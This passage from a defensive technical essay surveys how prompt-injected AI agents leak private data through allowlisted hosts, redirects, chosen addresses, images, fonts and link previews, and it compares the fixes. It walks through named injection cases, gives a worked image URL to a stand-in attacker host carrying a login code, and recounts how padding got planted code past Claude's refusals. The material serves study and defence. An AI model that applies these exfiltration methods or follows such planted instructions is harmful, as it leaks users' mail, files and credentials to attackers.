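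BeyondTrust reported the problem in September 2025. AWS deployed a fix in November, withdrew it the same month, and decided in December to change the documentation instead. It left lookups on because the sandbox needed to find Amazon's storage service. AWS closed the channel in April 2026, a month after BeyondTrust disclosed the problem publicly.

The proxy design described above avoids the problem because programs in the sandbox never look up outside names themselves. They pass each name to the proxy, which looks it up only if it is on the allowlist. An environment that needs lookups for other reasons can use a name server that answers only for allowlisted names. AWS customers could already get this by running the interpreter in a private network with a DNS firewall, though this took more setup.

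### When a trusted site forwards the request

The remaining failures involve requests that the allowlist was supposed to let through. Some were programming mistakes. Corgea's *Claude Code has a Domain Validation Bypass* reports that Claude Code's page-fetching tool checked only whether an address started with a trusted name. An attacker who owned `example.com` could therefore create `modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com` and pass it off as the documentation site for MCP. Comparing the whole host name prevents this.

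Redirects are harder to deal with, because the first request really does go to a trusted site. A redirect is a reply that tells the requesting software to go to another address, and websites routinely use them. For example, Bing's search results link to a bing.com address that counts the click and then forwards the visitor.

ChatGPT checks the links in its answers before it displays them, and in 2025 the check always approved bing.com. The security company Tenable realised that any page in Bing's index could therefore be reached through an approved bing.com address. These addresses break if altered, so an attacker couldn't add stolen data to them. Tenable's *HackedGPT* describes how the researchers got around this by getting a separate page indexed for each letter of the alphabet and having ChatGPT display the matching links in order, so that the sequence of visits spelled out the data. Some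 of the links were for images, which load without a click.

A request that encodes one of 26 letters carries at most log₂ 26 ≈ 4.7 bits. Leaking a long document this way would take thousands of requests, but a name or a password takes only a few. Data can leak even when the model is forbidden to change addresses, if the attacker has supplied a large enough set of them to choose from.

The fix for redirects is to check every address in the chain. A proxy that handles all connections does this automatically, because software that follows a redirect has to connect to the new host through the proxy. ChatGPT's check examined the link as written, before anything had followed it. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives redirects as a reason lists of trusted sites aren't enough.

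A proxy doesn't help when an allowed site fetches a blocked address itself. Translation services and link previewers do this from their own servers, where the proxy's egress rules don't apply.

### When the attacker has an account on a permitted service

In October 2025, the security researcher Johann Rehberger looked at the network settings for Claude's code sandbox. The default, "Package managers only", allowed a short list of hosts that programmers download software from. The first entry was `api.anthropic.com`, the address programs use to reach Anthropic's services. *Claude Pirate*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red, explains why allowing it was a security hole.

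Anthropic's services include file storage, and a request to store a file carries an API key, a credential that identifies an account. In the attack, a user asks Claude to summarise a document that contains planted instructions. Following them, Claude copies the user's last conversation into a file and uploads it with the attacker's API key. The proxy allows the request because the host is on the list of allowed sites, and the file is stored in the attacker's account. One upload can hold 30 megabytes. A 200-character web address carries about 150 bytes, so moving as much data that way would take 200,000 addresses.

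Claude often refused because an API key in the middle of a document looked suspicious. Rehberger got around this by padding the planted code with harmless lines. Anthropic closed Rehberger's report of the attack within an hour as a model safety matter outside the scope of its security programme. Five days later, Anthropic said this had been a mistake.

The vulnerability was still unfixed in January 2026, when Anthropic released Claude Cowork, an agent for office work that reads and edits files in a folder the user selects. Two days later, PromptArmor, a company that tests AI products, showed in *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* that the same attack worked there. In the demonstration, the user connected a folder of confidential property files and then added a Word document found online, which contained instructions in type too small and pale to notice. Cowork uploaded a loan estimate to the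 attacker's account without asking for approval. This demonstration used the small Claude Haiku model, but a version of the attack aimed at software developers also worked against Claude Opus 4.5, a much more resistant model.

Anthropic had to keep its own address on the list of allowed sites because Cowork doesn't work without it, so it added a decrypting proxy inside the virtual machine where Cowork runs code. The proxy passes requests to Anthropic's services only if they carry the token issued to that machine for that session, so a request with an attacker's key fails. It also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch another address, so an attacker can't use those servers to forward requests.

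The check has to happen on the user's side because Anthropic's servers can't distinguish a request from Cowork from one sent by another customer's program. But this puts the proxy in the same virtual machine as the code whose requests it checks. Code that took complete control of the machine might be able to bypass the proxy, though the outer list of hosts would presumably still apply.

Anthropic had thought of the allowlist as a filter on destinations, but drew the broader conclusion that each entry is permission to use every function the host offers. This seems correct. Adding `api.anthropic.com` so that the model could run had also permitted uploads to any Anthropic account.

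This can happen even when the service isn't public. In September 2026 Check Point Research reported another fault in ChatGPT's code sandbox. According to OffSeq's *The Shared Clipboard Inside the Sandbox* (2026), different users' containers shared an internal service that delivered software packages, through which they could pass messages to each other. An attacker with an ordinary account could send hidden tasks to a victim's session and get back data such as emails. eSecurity Planet's *ChatGPT Flaw Let Attackers Secretly Hijack a Victim’s AI Session* reports that OpenAI has since shut the service down. Companies often replace public package sites with an internal copy for safety, and this case suggests that the copy should be read-only or separate for each customer.

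### When a whole domain is approved for the sake of a few pages

Hugging Face is a website where anyone can publish AI models and data. Claude Code's page-fetching tool had `huggingface.co` on a built-in list of approved hosts, so it could open any page there without asking the user. GitLab's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026) describes how this approval covered every member's pages, including any that an attacker had just created.

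An attacker couldn't read Hugging Face's server logs, but could see the download counts that the site displays for certain files. To steal a six-digit login code, the attacker could publish 60 such files, ten for each digit, and have Claude fetch the six that match the code. The six counters that went up would reveal it. A filter that searches addresses for secrets would miss this because nothing in the requests looks like data.

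Expert Insights' *Researcher Finds Same Trust Flaw Across Claude Code, Gemini CLI, And Codex* describes how the researcher Meged came to use the counters. Meged first attacked Claude Code through shell commands. After Anthropic removed the agent's access to the shell, Meged got secrets out through commands that the software approved automatically because they only read data, and finally through Hugging Face. Anthropic fixed the problem in version 2.1.163, and MITRE's *CVE-2026-54316* lists every earlier version back to 0.2.54 as affected.

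The same mistake is easier to make with cloud hosting, where customers get names under a shared domain. ChatGPT's link check used to trust `windows.net`, which belongs to Microsoft. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* points out that anybody can open a Microsoft storage account, get an address under that domain, and read the log of requests to that address.

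### A rule for choosing destinations

These cases support a stricter rule than "allow only reputable sites". A destination is safe only if an attacker can neither receive data there nor make it forward data. Microsoft, Anthropic and Hugging Face are reputable, but their sites were unsafe to allow because outsiders could use them to collect data. Bing was unsafe because it forwarded visitors to pages that outsiders controlled.

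Receiving data has to include indirect ways of seeing it, such as a public counter. PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist?* (2026) goes through hosts that companies commonly approve and finds a way out through each:

- npm, from which programmers download JavaScript packages, also lets anyone with a free account publish one, so an agent can put stolen data in a package.
- GitHub accepts uploads to public repositories.
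- Google Docs shares its host name with Google Forms, and a form can take its answers from the web address.
- A wildcard such as `*.amazonaws.com` covers the storage of every Amazon cloud customer, the attacker included.

A strict reading of the rule excludes most of the useful web. A documentation site passes if it has no accounts, comments or public statistics and only its owner can read the logs. Very few of the hosts a coding agent needs meet these conditions. Docker's *Policies* describes a ready-made list called "Balanced", which permits AI providers, package managers, code hosts and container registries. These are the kinds of service that have leaked or that PromptArmor warns about. Docker warns that allowing `github.com` gives access to anything users have put there. Its alternative, "Locked Down", permits only what the user adds.

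A list like "Balanced" still blocks attackers who simply have data sent to their own server, which is the easiest attack to set up. But the operator of a feature that handles private data should assume that a determined attacker can get data out through such a list.

### Narrower permissions for each host

If a necessary host fails the rule, the operator can permit only part of what it offers. Replacing wildcards with exact host names is the easiest way to do this, because it works even with a proxy that doesn't decrypt traffic. For example, a company that keeps its files in one storage account can list that account's host name without allowing access to other customers' accounts.

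A proxy has to decrypt traffic to apply rules about methods and paths. It might allow only GET requests, which are meant for reading, to a code host or a package site. That would have stopped the upload to Anthropic's file storage, and it stops an agent from publishing a package. It wouldn't have stopped the leak through Hugging Face, where fetching a file was enough to raise the counter, and it doesn't stop submissions to a Google form that takes its answers from the URL. Those cases also need a rule about paths, such as one that permits only the files of two named models on the site.

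In October 2025, Rehberger proposed binding traffic to the customer's own account, and Anthropic later built roughly that. This works well for services that keep each account's data private. It works less well on GitHub, because an agent using its owner's account can still upload private files to a public repository, where the attacker can read them. The operator also has to block publishing, either at the proxy or by giving the agent a credential that can't publish.

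All this takes work for each host, and somebody has to update the rules as the services change. That is realistic for a coding agent that needs a dozen hosts or an invoice tool that needs two, but much less so for the mail assistant, whose user may book any hotel. OpenAI makes the same point about ChatGPT, whose users also visit lesser-known sites. It adds that a strict list produces frequent warnings, which people learn to click through. For automatic page loading, OpenAI therefore switched from checking whether it trusts the site to checking the exact address.

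## Allowing only addresses the model did not compose

When a model writes private data into a web address, the address is usually one that nobody has used before. Software can guard against such leaks by opening an exact address only if it came from somewhere other than the model, whichever site it leads to. The mail assistant could then open any hotel's page, however obscure, but it couldn't add a line of the user's mail to the end of the address.

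OpenAI and Anthropic have both built rules that allow only addresses the model did not compose. Researchers got around both sets of rules by having the model choose among ready-made addresses.

### ShadowLeak and the ban on altering addresses

In ChatGPT's Deep Research mode, an agent reads sources for up to half an hour and then writes a report. Users can connect it to their Gmail accounts. *ShadowLeak*, a report by the network security vendor Radware, describes how a single email could make the agent send out private data from the mailbox.

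The email told the agent to find an employee's name and home address in the other messages, and to open a supposed staff lookup page with those details in the web address. The page was on a server that the researchers treated as the attacker's. With early versions of the email, the agent refused, or opened the page without the details. It complied once the email also told it to encode the details first, supposedly to keep them secure. According to Radware, this worked because the model encoded the details before passing the request on, so the software that carried out the request saw only a harmless-looking string.

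The final version worked every time in Radware's tests. But it closely resembles the restructuring email that OpenAI says worked half the time, so the true success rate is uncertain.

ChatGPT already checked the links and images it displayed, but Radware found no comparable limit on the addresses the agent could open from OpenAI's servers. The victim's employer couldn't have spotted the leak, because the request never crossed its network. Radware reported the flaw in June 2025, and OpenAI fixed it in early August.

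To remedy this, OpenAI let ChatGPT open addresses only as it had received them. ChatGPT could no longer add anything to the end of an address, even when told to.

### ZombieAgent's alphabet of addresses

In late September 2025, Radware's researcher Zvika Babo reported a way around the ban. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes an attack in which the attacker's email contains 37 complete addresses, one for each letter, one for each digit and one for a space. To send a name, ChatGPT opens the matching addresses in order, and the attacker reads the name from the server log. The ban had no effect on this, because ChatGPT never altered an address.

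Requests can arrive out of order, which would scramble the name, so Babo gave each character a separate address for every position. An A in third place, for example, had a different address from an A in fifth. This also meant that ChatGPT never had to open the same address twice. A 20-character string would need 37 × 20 = 740 addresses, which a short script can generate.

The basic idea dates back to at least 2023, when Johann Rehberger described a leak that used one address per letter, as he recalls in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. Tenable had also used it to build its alphabet of Bing links. The method works because the software checks each request separately, and each one looks harmless on its own, as did the pieces of a split secret in the experiment by Lan and colleagues.

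OpenAI also restricted addresses by where they came from, so ChatGPT would not open one that an attacker had planted in its memory. Babo got around this by planting an instruction in memory to read a particular email whenever the user sent a message. The email supplied the addresses, which ChatGPT could open. The theft could continue in every later conversation, even though the user had opened the attacker's file only once.

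OpenAI fixed the vulnerability on December 16, 2025, almost three months after it was first reported. After the fix, ChatGPT would open a link from an email only if it appeared in a well-known public index, according to the news report *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*.

### OpenAI's rule: the address must already be public

In January 2026, OpenAI explained the general rule. It applies when ChatGPT loads something automatically, such as an article it wants to read or an image for its answer:

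1. A crawler, which is a program that explores the web as a search engine does, records the public addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. ChatGPT prepares to load an address.
3. The software looks for that exact address in the crawler's records.
4. If the address is there, ChatGPT loads it without asking.
5. If the address is missing, the software either tells the model to try another site or shows the user a warning, and loads nothing unless the user agrees.

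The crawler has no access to users' conversations, so it cannot have obtained an address from one. An address that was already public is therefore much less likely to contain the user's private data.

The mail assistant would work fairly well under this rule. The crawler has probably visited the hotel's page about arrival times, so the assistant could open it. But the crawler almost certainly hasn't visited the link in the confirmation email, which contains the booking number, so the assistant would probably be blocked from opening it. Opening it would leak nothing, because the hotel wrote the link and already knows the number, but the rule doesn't distinguish this link from one that an attacker wants the assistant to open.

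OpenAI promises only that the agent will not quietly leak user-specific data through the address. It says that a page can still contain untrustworthy content, attempts to manipulate the user or harmful instructions. An instruction planted on a well-known page therefore reaches the model as easily as it would without the restriction.

Even the rule's narrow promise has a gap, which OpenAI's technical paper on it acknowledges. An attacker can still leak data by having the model request one address per letter, if the crawler has already seen all the addresses. Embrace The Red points out that anyone with a large website or blog probably has 36 pages in the index already, and can use planted text to tell the model which page stands for which character. This vocabulary could even run to thousands of pages.

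The rule does make the attack harder to prepare. ZombieAgent's addresses could be made up on the spot, but an attacker now needs pages that the crawler has already visited. An attacker therefore can't use a new server right away, but can wait until the crawler reaches it.

Every part of the product also has to apply the rule. Rehberger recalls that ChatGPT's older link check was missing from the macOS and iOS apps, and thinks some OpenAI developers may not know about the new one. ShadowLeak shows why this matters, since OpenAI had been checking displayed links for more than a year when Radware found that Deep Research could open any address.

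### Anthropic's rule: the address must already be in the conversation

Anthropic's web fetch tool, which it released to developers in September 2025, doesn't consult an index of the web. It looks at where an address has appeared in the conversation. The documentation from Anthropic describes a procedure that, before a change in July 2026, ran roughly as follows:

1. Addresses enter the conversation in the user's messages, in the results of tools that the developer runs, and in the results of earlier searches and page fetches.
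2. The model asks the web fetch tool to open an address.
3. The tool checks whether the address has appeared in any of those places. If it hasn't, the tool refuses.
4. If it has, the tool returns the text of the page. Any links on that page become addresses that the model may open next.

Addresses in the output of code that the model runs on Anthropic's servers do not count as having appeared in the conversation. Otherwise, the model could get around the rule by writing a one-line program that prints an address containing the user's data.

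The restriction is meant to stop the model from sending data out by writing it into an address. Anthropic says that some risk remains, and advises developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. Developers worried about data theft can turn the tool off, limit it to certain sites or cap the number of fetches.

Willison (2025), in *Claude API*, identified a weakness as soon as the tool came out. In Anthropic's interface for developers, a "user message" is whatever the developer's software submits under that label, and many applications paste other people's text into it. Results from the developer's own tools can also contain other people's text. The mail assistant's mailbox search is one of those tools, so once it returned a stranger's email, every web address in that email would be permitted, including a list like ZombieAgent's.

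Willison still thought that refusing addresses the model had composed gave the most protection, because the common attacks depend on them. That seems right, although he wrote this before ZombieAgent came out.

Anthropic's rule is more convenient than OpenAI's for private links. The assistant could open the hotel's booking link because it arrived in the user's mail. But the rule also lets an attacker add permitted addresses by sending an email, without waiting for a crawler.

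### The Memory Heist

*The Memory Heist* (Ayush Paul, July 2026) showed that a web page could add permitted addresses too. Paul tested the ordinary Claude chat app with no mailbox connected. The app still had access to plenty of private information that an attacker could steal, because it summarised the user's recent conversations every day, put the summary into each new conversation, and could search older ones.

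Paul first asked Claude to open a test site with his own name added to the address, and the web fetch tool blocked the request. But the tool could follow links on pages it had already fetched, and Paul controlled the links on the test site.

Paul set up the site so that Claude could spell out text by following links. The home page linked to one page for each letter. The page for A linked to AA, AB, AC and so on, and each of those linked to pages one letter longer. The server created each page when Claude requested it. Claude spelled out `ayush-paul` in ten clicks, and the last address contained the whole name. The model composed none of the addresses, but by choosing which links to follow, it still produced the kind of address the rule was meant to prevent.

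In this first test, Paul had asked Claude to spell the name, whereas a real attacker's site would have to persuade Claude to do it. Claude treated several cover stories as suspicious, including a loyalty scheme, but it accepted a fake security check on a coffee shop's site, which instructed AI assistants to identify their user by following the links. The site then also got Claude to reveal the user's employer and home town.

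The site showed the fake check only to visitors whose requests identified them as Claude, so a person opening the same address would have seen an ordinary shop. Hackaday's *This Week In Security* (2026) notes that asking Claude to summarise the site was enough to set off the attack.

Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally. Willison (2026) reports in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* that the company then stopped the tool from following links in pages it had fetched. Hostile sites can therefore no longer create new permitted addresses during an attack.

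The chat app can still open addresses that the user typed or that a web search returned. An attacker could try to get a page for each letter of the alphabet into the search results, which would take about as much preparation as getting them into OpenAI's index. The change makes the app somewhat less convenient, since Claude can no longer follow a link from a table of contents to a chapter unless a search also returns the chapter.

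### How much a choice among fixed addresses can carry

ZombieAgent and the Memory Heist both replaced writing with choosing, and there is a firm limit on what choosing can leak. Suppose the model may open N addresses and makes k requests. The first request has N possible outcomes. Two requests in order have N × N, and k requests have Nᵏ. The attacker sees which of these sequences occurred, and so learns at most

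log₂(Nᵏ) = k · log₂ N bits.

No clever encoding can beat this, because the attacker's log can't tell apart more than Nᵏ cases.

For ZombieAgent's 37 addresses and 20 requests, the limit is

20 × log₂ 37 ≈ 20 × 5.21 ≈ 104 bits.

That is just enough to encode any string of 20 letters, digits and spaces. Paul's pages each offered 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen, so ten clicks could carry about 48 bits.

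With 37 fixed addresses, sending the 1,200 bits that fit in 200 freely written characters would take 231 requests, and sending a thousand words of mail would take more than 9,000. A rule against composed addresses therefore protects long documents well but short secrets much less well, since a six-digit login code needs only four requests.

The attacker can also use a longer list. With 1,024 addresses, each request carries 10 bits, so the 20-character string needs 11 requests instead of 20. An address can also stand for a whole fact instead of a character. To learn where the user works, an attacker could prepare one page for each of 1,024 large employers and get the answer from a single request.

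The formula counts only which addresses the model opens and in what order, so an attacker who also uses the timing of the requests may learn more. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (2026) considers an attacker who does not know what the user asked for. The attacker adds a link or pop-up to a page the agent is reading, which leads it to a probing website, and records the number, order and timing of its requests there. The agent's ordinary choice of pages could reveal something about the user's task, even if nobody told it to send data.

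### Whether caching, repeat bans and caps would help

Rehberger suggests two measures against alphabets of addresses. The software could cache each page, keeping a copy and reusing it for a few minutes, or refuse to visit the same address twice in one session. Either way, the attacker's server would receive at most one request for each address.

Limiting the model to opening each address only once reduces the amount it can leak only slightly. With 37 addresses and 20 requests, the number of possible sequences falls from 37²⁰ to 37 × 36 × … × 18, which still leaves about 95 bits. If the requests also arrive in a jumbled order, the attacker learns only which 20 of the 37 addresses the model opened. That leaves about 34 bits, which is still enough for a ten-digit phone number.

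| Addresses available | Requests | What the attacker sees | Most they can carry |
|---|---|---|---|
| 37 | 20 | Every visit, in order | 104 bits |
| 37 | 20 | One visit per address, in order | 95 bits |
| 37 | 20 | One visit per address, order lost | 34 bits |
| 740 | 20 | One visit per address, order lost | 129 bits |
| 1,024 | 11 | Every visit, in order | 110 bits |
| 1,024 | 3 | Every visit, in order | 30 bits |

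A simple attack would leak less than these figures suggest. If the model spells out the name Anna, the attacker receives only an A and an N. To leak close to 95 bits, the model would have to use a complicated code that never repeats an address, and the model might make mistakes in using it.

But an attacker with more addresses doesn't need a complicated code. ZombieAgent's 740 numbered addresses can carry a 20-character string without any repeats, whatever order the requests arrive in. Paul's nested pages have the same advantage, because each address contains the whole of the previous one plus one more character. Caching and repeat bans are therefore useful only where extra addresses are hard to get. They would strengthen OpenAI's index rule somewhat, but would add very little to a rule that allows addresses supplied by an email.

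In theory, capping the number of requests works better than capping the number of addresses. The leak is proportional to the number of requests but only to the logarithm of the number of addresses, so an attacker with half as many requests needs the square of the number of addresses to leak the same amount. Sending any 20-character string takes 37² = 1,369 addresses with ten requests, 37⁴ or about 1.9 million with five, and about 28 billion with three. Very few attackers could get even 1.9 million addresses into a public index.

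A cap on requests again protects short secrets poorly. With 1,000 addresses to choose from, two requests are enough to leak a six-digit code, so a cap that protected the code would have to stop the assistant after one page. Deep Research could hardly work under a cap of five pages, let alone one.

Anthropic lets developers cap the number of fetches the web fetch tool makes, but sets no cap by default. The examples in its documentation use caps of five and ten. The cap applies separately to each request from the developer's software to Claude, so a conversation with many turns can include many more fetches. The planted memory in ZombieAgent is a reason to count fetches over a longer period, since an attack that sends four characters before each answer could send a lot of text in a week.

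Anthropic's tool also rejects addresses of more than 250 characters. This limit would matter if the model could write the address, but when the model can only choose from a list of 37, its choice carries 5.2 bits regardless of the address's length.

OpenAI offers a much stricter form of caching. In Lockdown Mode, an optional setting for people and organisations at particular risk, ChatGPT can browse only copies of pages that OpenAI already holds. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* says that no live request leaves its network while the model browses. In terms of the formula, k is zero, and the attacker learns nothing from the model's choice of pages. This holds only if OpenAI makes the copies independently of the model's requests. If a request for a missing page caused OpenAI to fetch it, the choice would leak.

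OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* warns that search results may be out of date or missing, and that a cached page can still contain a planted instruction that affects the answer. OpenAI says most users don't need the setting. With it on, the mail assistant could still answer the original question, because a hotel seldom changes its check-in time, but it couldn't find out whether the hotel has a room free tonight.

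## Requests made by the user's screen: images, links and previews

A mail assistant with no web tool can still leak data through a web request. The program that displays its answer, usually a browser or a chat app, sends its own requests to load images and preview links. Restrictions on the model's tools don't affect these requests.

### From the model's text to the attacker's log

Most chat products let the model format its answers in Markdown, a notation in which a few punctuation marks stand for a heading, a link or an image. To include an image, the model writes only the picture's web address. Suppose a planted email persuades the mail assistant to end its answer with one:

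1. The model finds a login code in the mailbox and writes the markup for an image at `attacker.example/dot.png?d=483920`.
2. The assistant's server sends the answer to the user's browser as text. The model hasn't called a web tool, so software that checks such calls has nothing to check.
3. Code on the chat page converts the Markdown to HTML, the language of web pages, and the markup becomes an image element.
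4. The browser requests the address at once, as it would for a picture on any other page.
5. The attacker's server records the address, login code included, and returns a single transparent pixel.

The user sees an ordinary answer. The request comes from the user's own device, so it never passes through an egress proxy around the model's code environment.

Johann Rehberger demonstrated this in 2023 on Bing Chat, Microsoft's search assistant, which could read the page a user had open. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* describes how a comment or an advertisement on that page could take control of the conversation. A couple of turns later, the model produced an image whose address contained a short encoded summary of the page and the conversation, plus a secret from the page.

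The flaw keeps coming back in new products. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, 2026) describes an attack on Google Antigravity, a coding program whose agent can read web pages and the secrets stored in a developer's environment. The attacker puts instructions in a web page's title, disguised as an error log, and an image in the chat carries the data out.

### Microsoft's early fix: a policy for the page

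Rehberger reported the Bing Chat flaw in April 2023, and Microsoft told him on June 15 that the flaw was fixed. Judging by his tests, the fix relied at least partly on a Content Security Policy (CSP), a set of rules that a website sends to the browser along with a page. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the draft standard, defines how a policy limits what the page may load and from where.

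A policy might include the rule `img-src 'self' *.bing.com`, which permits images from the page's own site and from any host under bing.com. Before loading an image, the browser compares its address with this list and sends no request if nothing matches. A policy can have separate lists for images, fonts, scripts and other kinds of content.

This is an allowlist, enforced by the browser. It would block the image in the example above, but an attacker who can use an allowed host can get around it. Google's policy for its Bard assistant restricted images to google.com and its subdomains. Willison's *Hacking Google Bard* explains that anybody could run a small program on one of those subdomains, `script.google.com`, and use it to collect data.

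Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant, had a similar problem more than two years later. Its policy permitted `docs.google.com`, which also hosts Google Forms. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack in which the assistant displayed an image whose address was a filled-in form. When the browser tried to load the image, Google recorded a form submission that the attacker could read. One answer leaked parts of more than 40 emails. PromptArmor reported the attack on a Friday night in December 2025, and Superhuman switched off the vulnerable features the following Monday. According to PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data*, the same method worked on OpenAI's Codex the next spring. OpenAI has since fixed it.

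### EchoLeak: a permitted site that fetches other sites

An attacker can use a permitted host that fetches addresses on request, even if the host stores nothing for the attacker. EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) used such a host against Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that searches a company's mail and files. Aim Security found the attack in January 2025, and Reddy and Gujral (2025) reconstruct it from public accounts in *EchoLeak*.

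The attacker only had to send an email. Microsoft's classifier for planted instructions missed it because it was worded as a request to its human recipient. When the user later asked Copilot a question, Copilot retrieved the email and put confidential data into an image address in its answer. Copilot's filter for removing outside links missed Markdown's "reference" style, which puts the address on a separate line below the text.

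The page's policy would still have blocked an image from the attacker's server. Aim Security therefore used a Microsoft Teams preview service, which was on the permitted list and would fetch any address it received. The browser contacted Teams, which then contacted the attacker's server. Microsoft fixed the flaw by May 2025 and found no sign that anyone had exploited it.

### SearchLeak

A year later, the security company Varonis found an attack chain with much the same result in Copilot's Enterprise Search. It is tracked as CVE-2026-42824, and Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) explains its three parts.

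The attack started with a link to Copilot's search page. The page could take its query from the web address, and Copilot treated this text as instructions as well as search terms. An attacker could therefore write instructions into a link and send it by email or chat, and the model would take them for the user's own, as in Anthropic's phishing exercise. The link led to a real Microsoft site, so a filter that checks only a site's reputation would not block it. When the victim clicked, Copilot searched the mailbox with the victim's permissions and put an email's title into the address of an image.

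As a safeguard against markup in Copilot's answers, Microsoft wrapped each answer in a code block, which makes the browser show markup as plain text. But Copilot's answers appear piece by piece, and Microsoft's code wrapped them only once they were complete. Until then, the browser treated each piece as live HTML, so it requested the picture before the image element was wrapped. This is a race condition, meaning that the result depends on which of two events happens first.

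The page's policy would have blocked a request to the attacker's server, but it permitted every host under bing.com. Bing's image search accepts the address of a picture, and Bing's servers then fetch and analyse the picture. The planted instructions therefore had Copilot write an image address that pointed to Bing's image search and gave the attacker's address as the picture to analyse. The attacker's address included the email's title. The browser contacted Bing, and Bing's server then contacted the attacker's, a form of SSRF aimed at an external server. In Varonis' demonstration, the attacker's log showed a request for `/Your_Security_Code_847291/img.png`.

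A leaked email title can expose a login code, because many services put codes there. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* notes that these codes often stay valid for several minutes. The attack could also reach calendar entries and any company files the victim could search.

Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), published on June 4, rates the flaw critical but gives it a severity score of 6.5 out of 10. The Next Web says the score is modest because the attack requires a click. Microsoft reports no exploitation. It had already fixed the service, so customers had nothing to install.

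### Which repair would have broken the chain

Varonis notes that the attack needed all three weaknesses, so fixing any one would have stopped it. But some fixes would have been easier to bypass than others.

If Copilot had treated the text in the link only as search terms, an attacker could still have tried sending the instructions in an email, as in EchoLeak. If Microsoft had removed Bing from the permitted list, the attacker would have needed another permitted service that fetches addresses, like the one Aim Security had found in Teams the year before. Microsoft's 2023 policy for Bing Chat had already permitted `www.bing.com`.

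Neutralising the markup before the browser displayed it seems the best single fix, because it would have stopped the image regardless of how the instructions arrived or which address the image used. Varonis recommends cleaning output when it is displayed and checking whether any permitted domains fetch addresses supplied by users. Microsoft says only that it has fully mitigated the flaw. Its record classifies the flaw as command injection, which fits the link's text better than it fits the image or Bing.

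### Images are not the only things a page loads

Cleaning HTML works only if it covers everything that makes a browser send a request. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes a Microsoft 365 Copilot feature that displayed HTML inside the chat. Microsoft removed image elements from the HTML, but when Rehberger asked Copilot for other ways to load external content, it produced a style sheet (the part of a page that sets its appearance) that requested a background image.

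The page's policy blocked some of these requests, but Copilot runs inside many Microsoft products, and each host page had its own policy. Fonts were an easier route because the font lists were looser and let the browser contact Rehberger's server. In one demonstration, a user opened a shared Word document and typed "hi there", and Copilot sent out the contents of an email in the address of a font. The HTML preview was hidden by default, but planted text could get Copilot to open it.

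Rehberger reported this in October 2025, and Microsoft finished fixing it in March 2026. He concludes that CSP isn't a reliable boundary for Copilot. The lists of permitted domains he saw were long, and individual employees seemed to have added some of the entries. W3C also recommends CSP only as a further layer of defence, behind careful handling of input and output.

If an assistant's maker relies on its own site's policy to restrict web requests, that protection may disappear when a customer embeds the assistant in a page with a looser policy.

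### Link previews in messaging apps

People also talk to AI agents through messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram, which often fetch linked pages to show previews. When the model has written the link, this fetch sends out any data the model put in the URL. In the Silent Egress experiment, a preview instead brought planted instructions to the model.

Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* shows this for Slack, which by default previews links posted by apps as well as by people. Soon after a test message appeared, the linked server logged a request from Slack's link-fetching program. The request didn't come from the user's browser, so no page policy applied to it, and a log of the user's network traffic wouldn't have shown it.

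In February 2026 PromptArmor set up a public website where people could test their own agents. When a user's agent posted a link to the site in a messaging app, the site showed whether the app had fetched a preview and what data had arrived with the request. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reports that OpenClaw, an agent people can reach through messaging apps, was exposed in its default setup on Telegram. Apostol's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* also lists Slack, Discord, and Microsoft Teams with agents built in Copilot Studio. Volunteers chose what to test and reported which agent they had used, so the results show that these combinations can leak but not how common the problem is.

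Switching previews off is easy where the app allows it. A Slack developer can set `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false on each message the agent posts. OpenClaw has a `linkPreview` setting for Telegram, and PromptArmor found that turning it off stopped the leak. But many users will never change a default, and OpenClaw's Telegram documentation still listed previews as on by default in June 2026. PromptArmor would like messaging apps to offer the setting for individual chats and channels, so people could keep previews everywhere except where an agent posts.

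A message can also contain images, which this setting may not cover. Copilot Cowork, Microsoft's agent for office work, normally asks for approval before it sends a message, but not when the recipient is its own user. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (May 2026) describes an attack that used this exception. Planted instructions made the agent send its user a Teams message containing remote images, which loaded when the user opened the message. The attack worked in all five trials.

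The image addresses in that attack contained download links, which let anyone who has them download a file without signing in. A short address could therefore expose a whole document.

### Blocking images, or passing them through a proxy

The simplest remedy is to load no remote images. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) explains that Gemini doesn't display external images, so EchoLeak's image step wouldn't work on it. The mail assistant would lose little without them, but a travel assistant that can't show pictures of hotels would be noticeably worse. The product can still show images that it stores itself, as long as its image server won't fetch anything else on request.

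A product that needs outside images can load them through a proxy that accepts only known addresses. GitHub uses one called Camo. When someone publishes a document with an outside image, GitHub replaces the image's address with a Camo address that includes a cryptographic signature. Camo fetches the image only if the signature is valid. A model can't produce a valid signature, so it can't make up a new Camo address that contains private data.

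But it can choose among addresses that GitHub has already signed. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes an attack on GitHub's Copilot Chat that used a signed address for each letter and symbol. The attacker put the list of addresses in an invisible comment on a proposed code change. When a user asked Copilot about the change, Copilot displayed images in an order that spelled out text from the user's private projects. In one test, the attack leaked the description of an unpublished security flaw. This is the alphabet attack again, and it suits images particularly well because one answer can hold many transparent pixels. A cap on the number of pages the model may fetch wouldn't limit them. GitHub fixed the problem in August 2025 by no longer displaying images in Copilot Chat.

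A proxy that accepts any address is much worse than Camo, because an attacker can use it to relay requests, as with Teams and Bing. The assistant in Notion, a note-taking service, could leak data through images. PromptArmor advised Notion to require the user's approval for external images and to make sure that its own image server couldn't redirect requests past the page's policy.

### Cleaning the output before display

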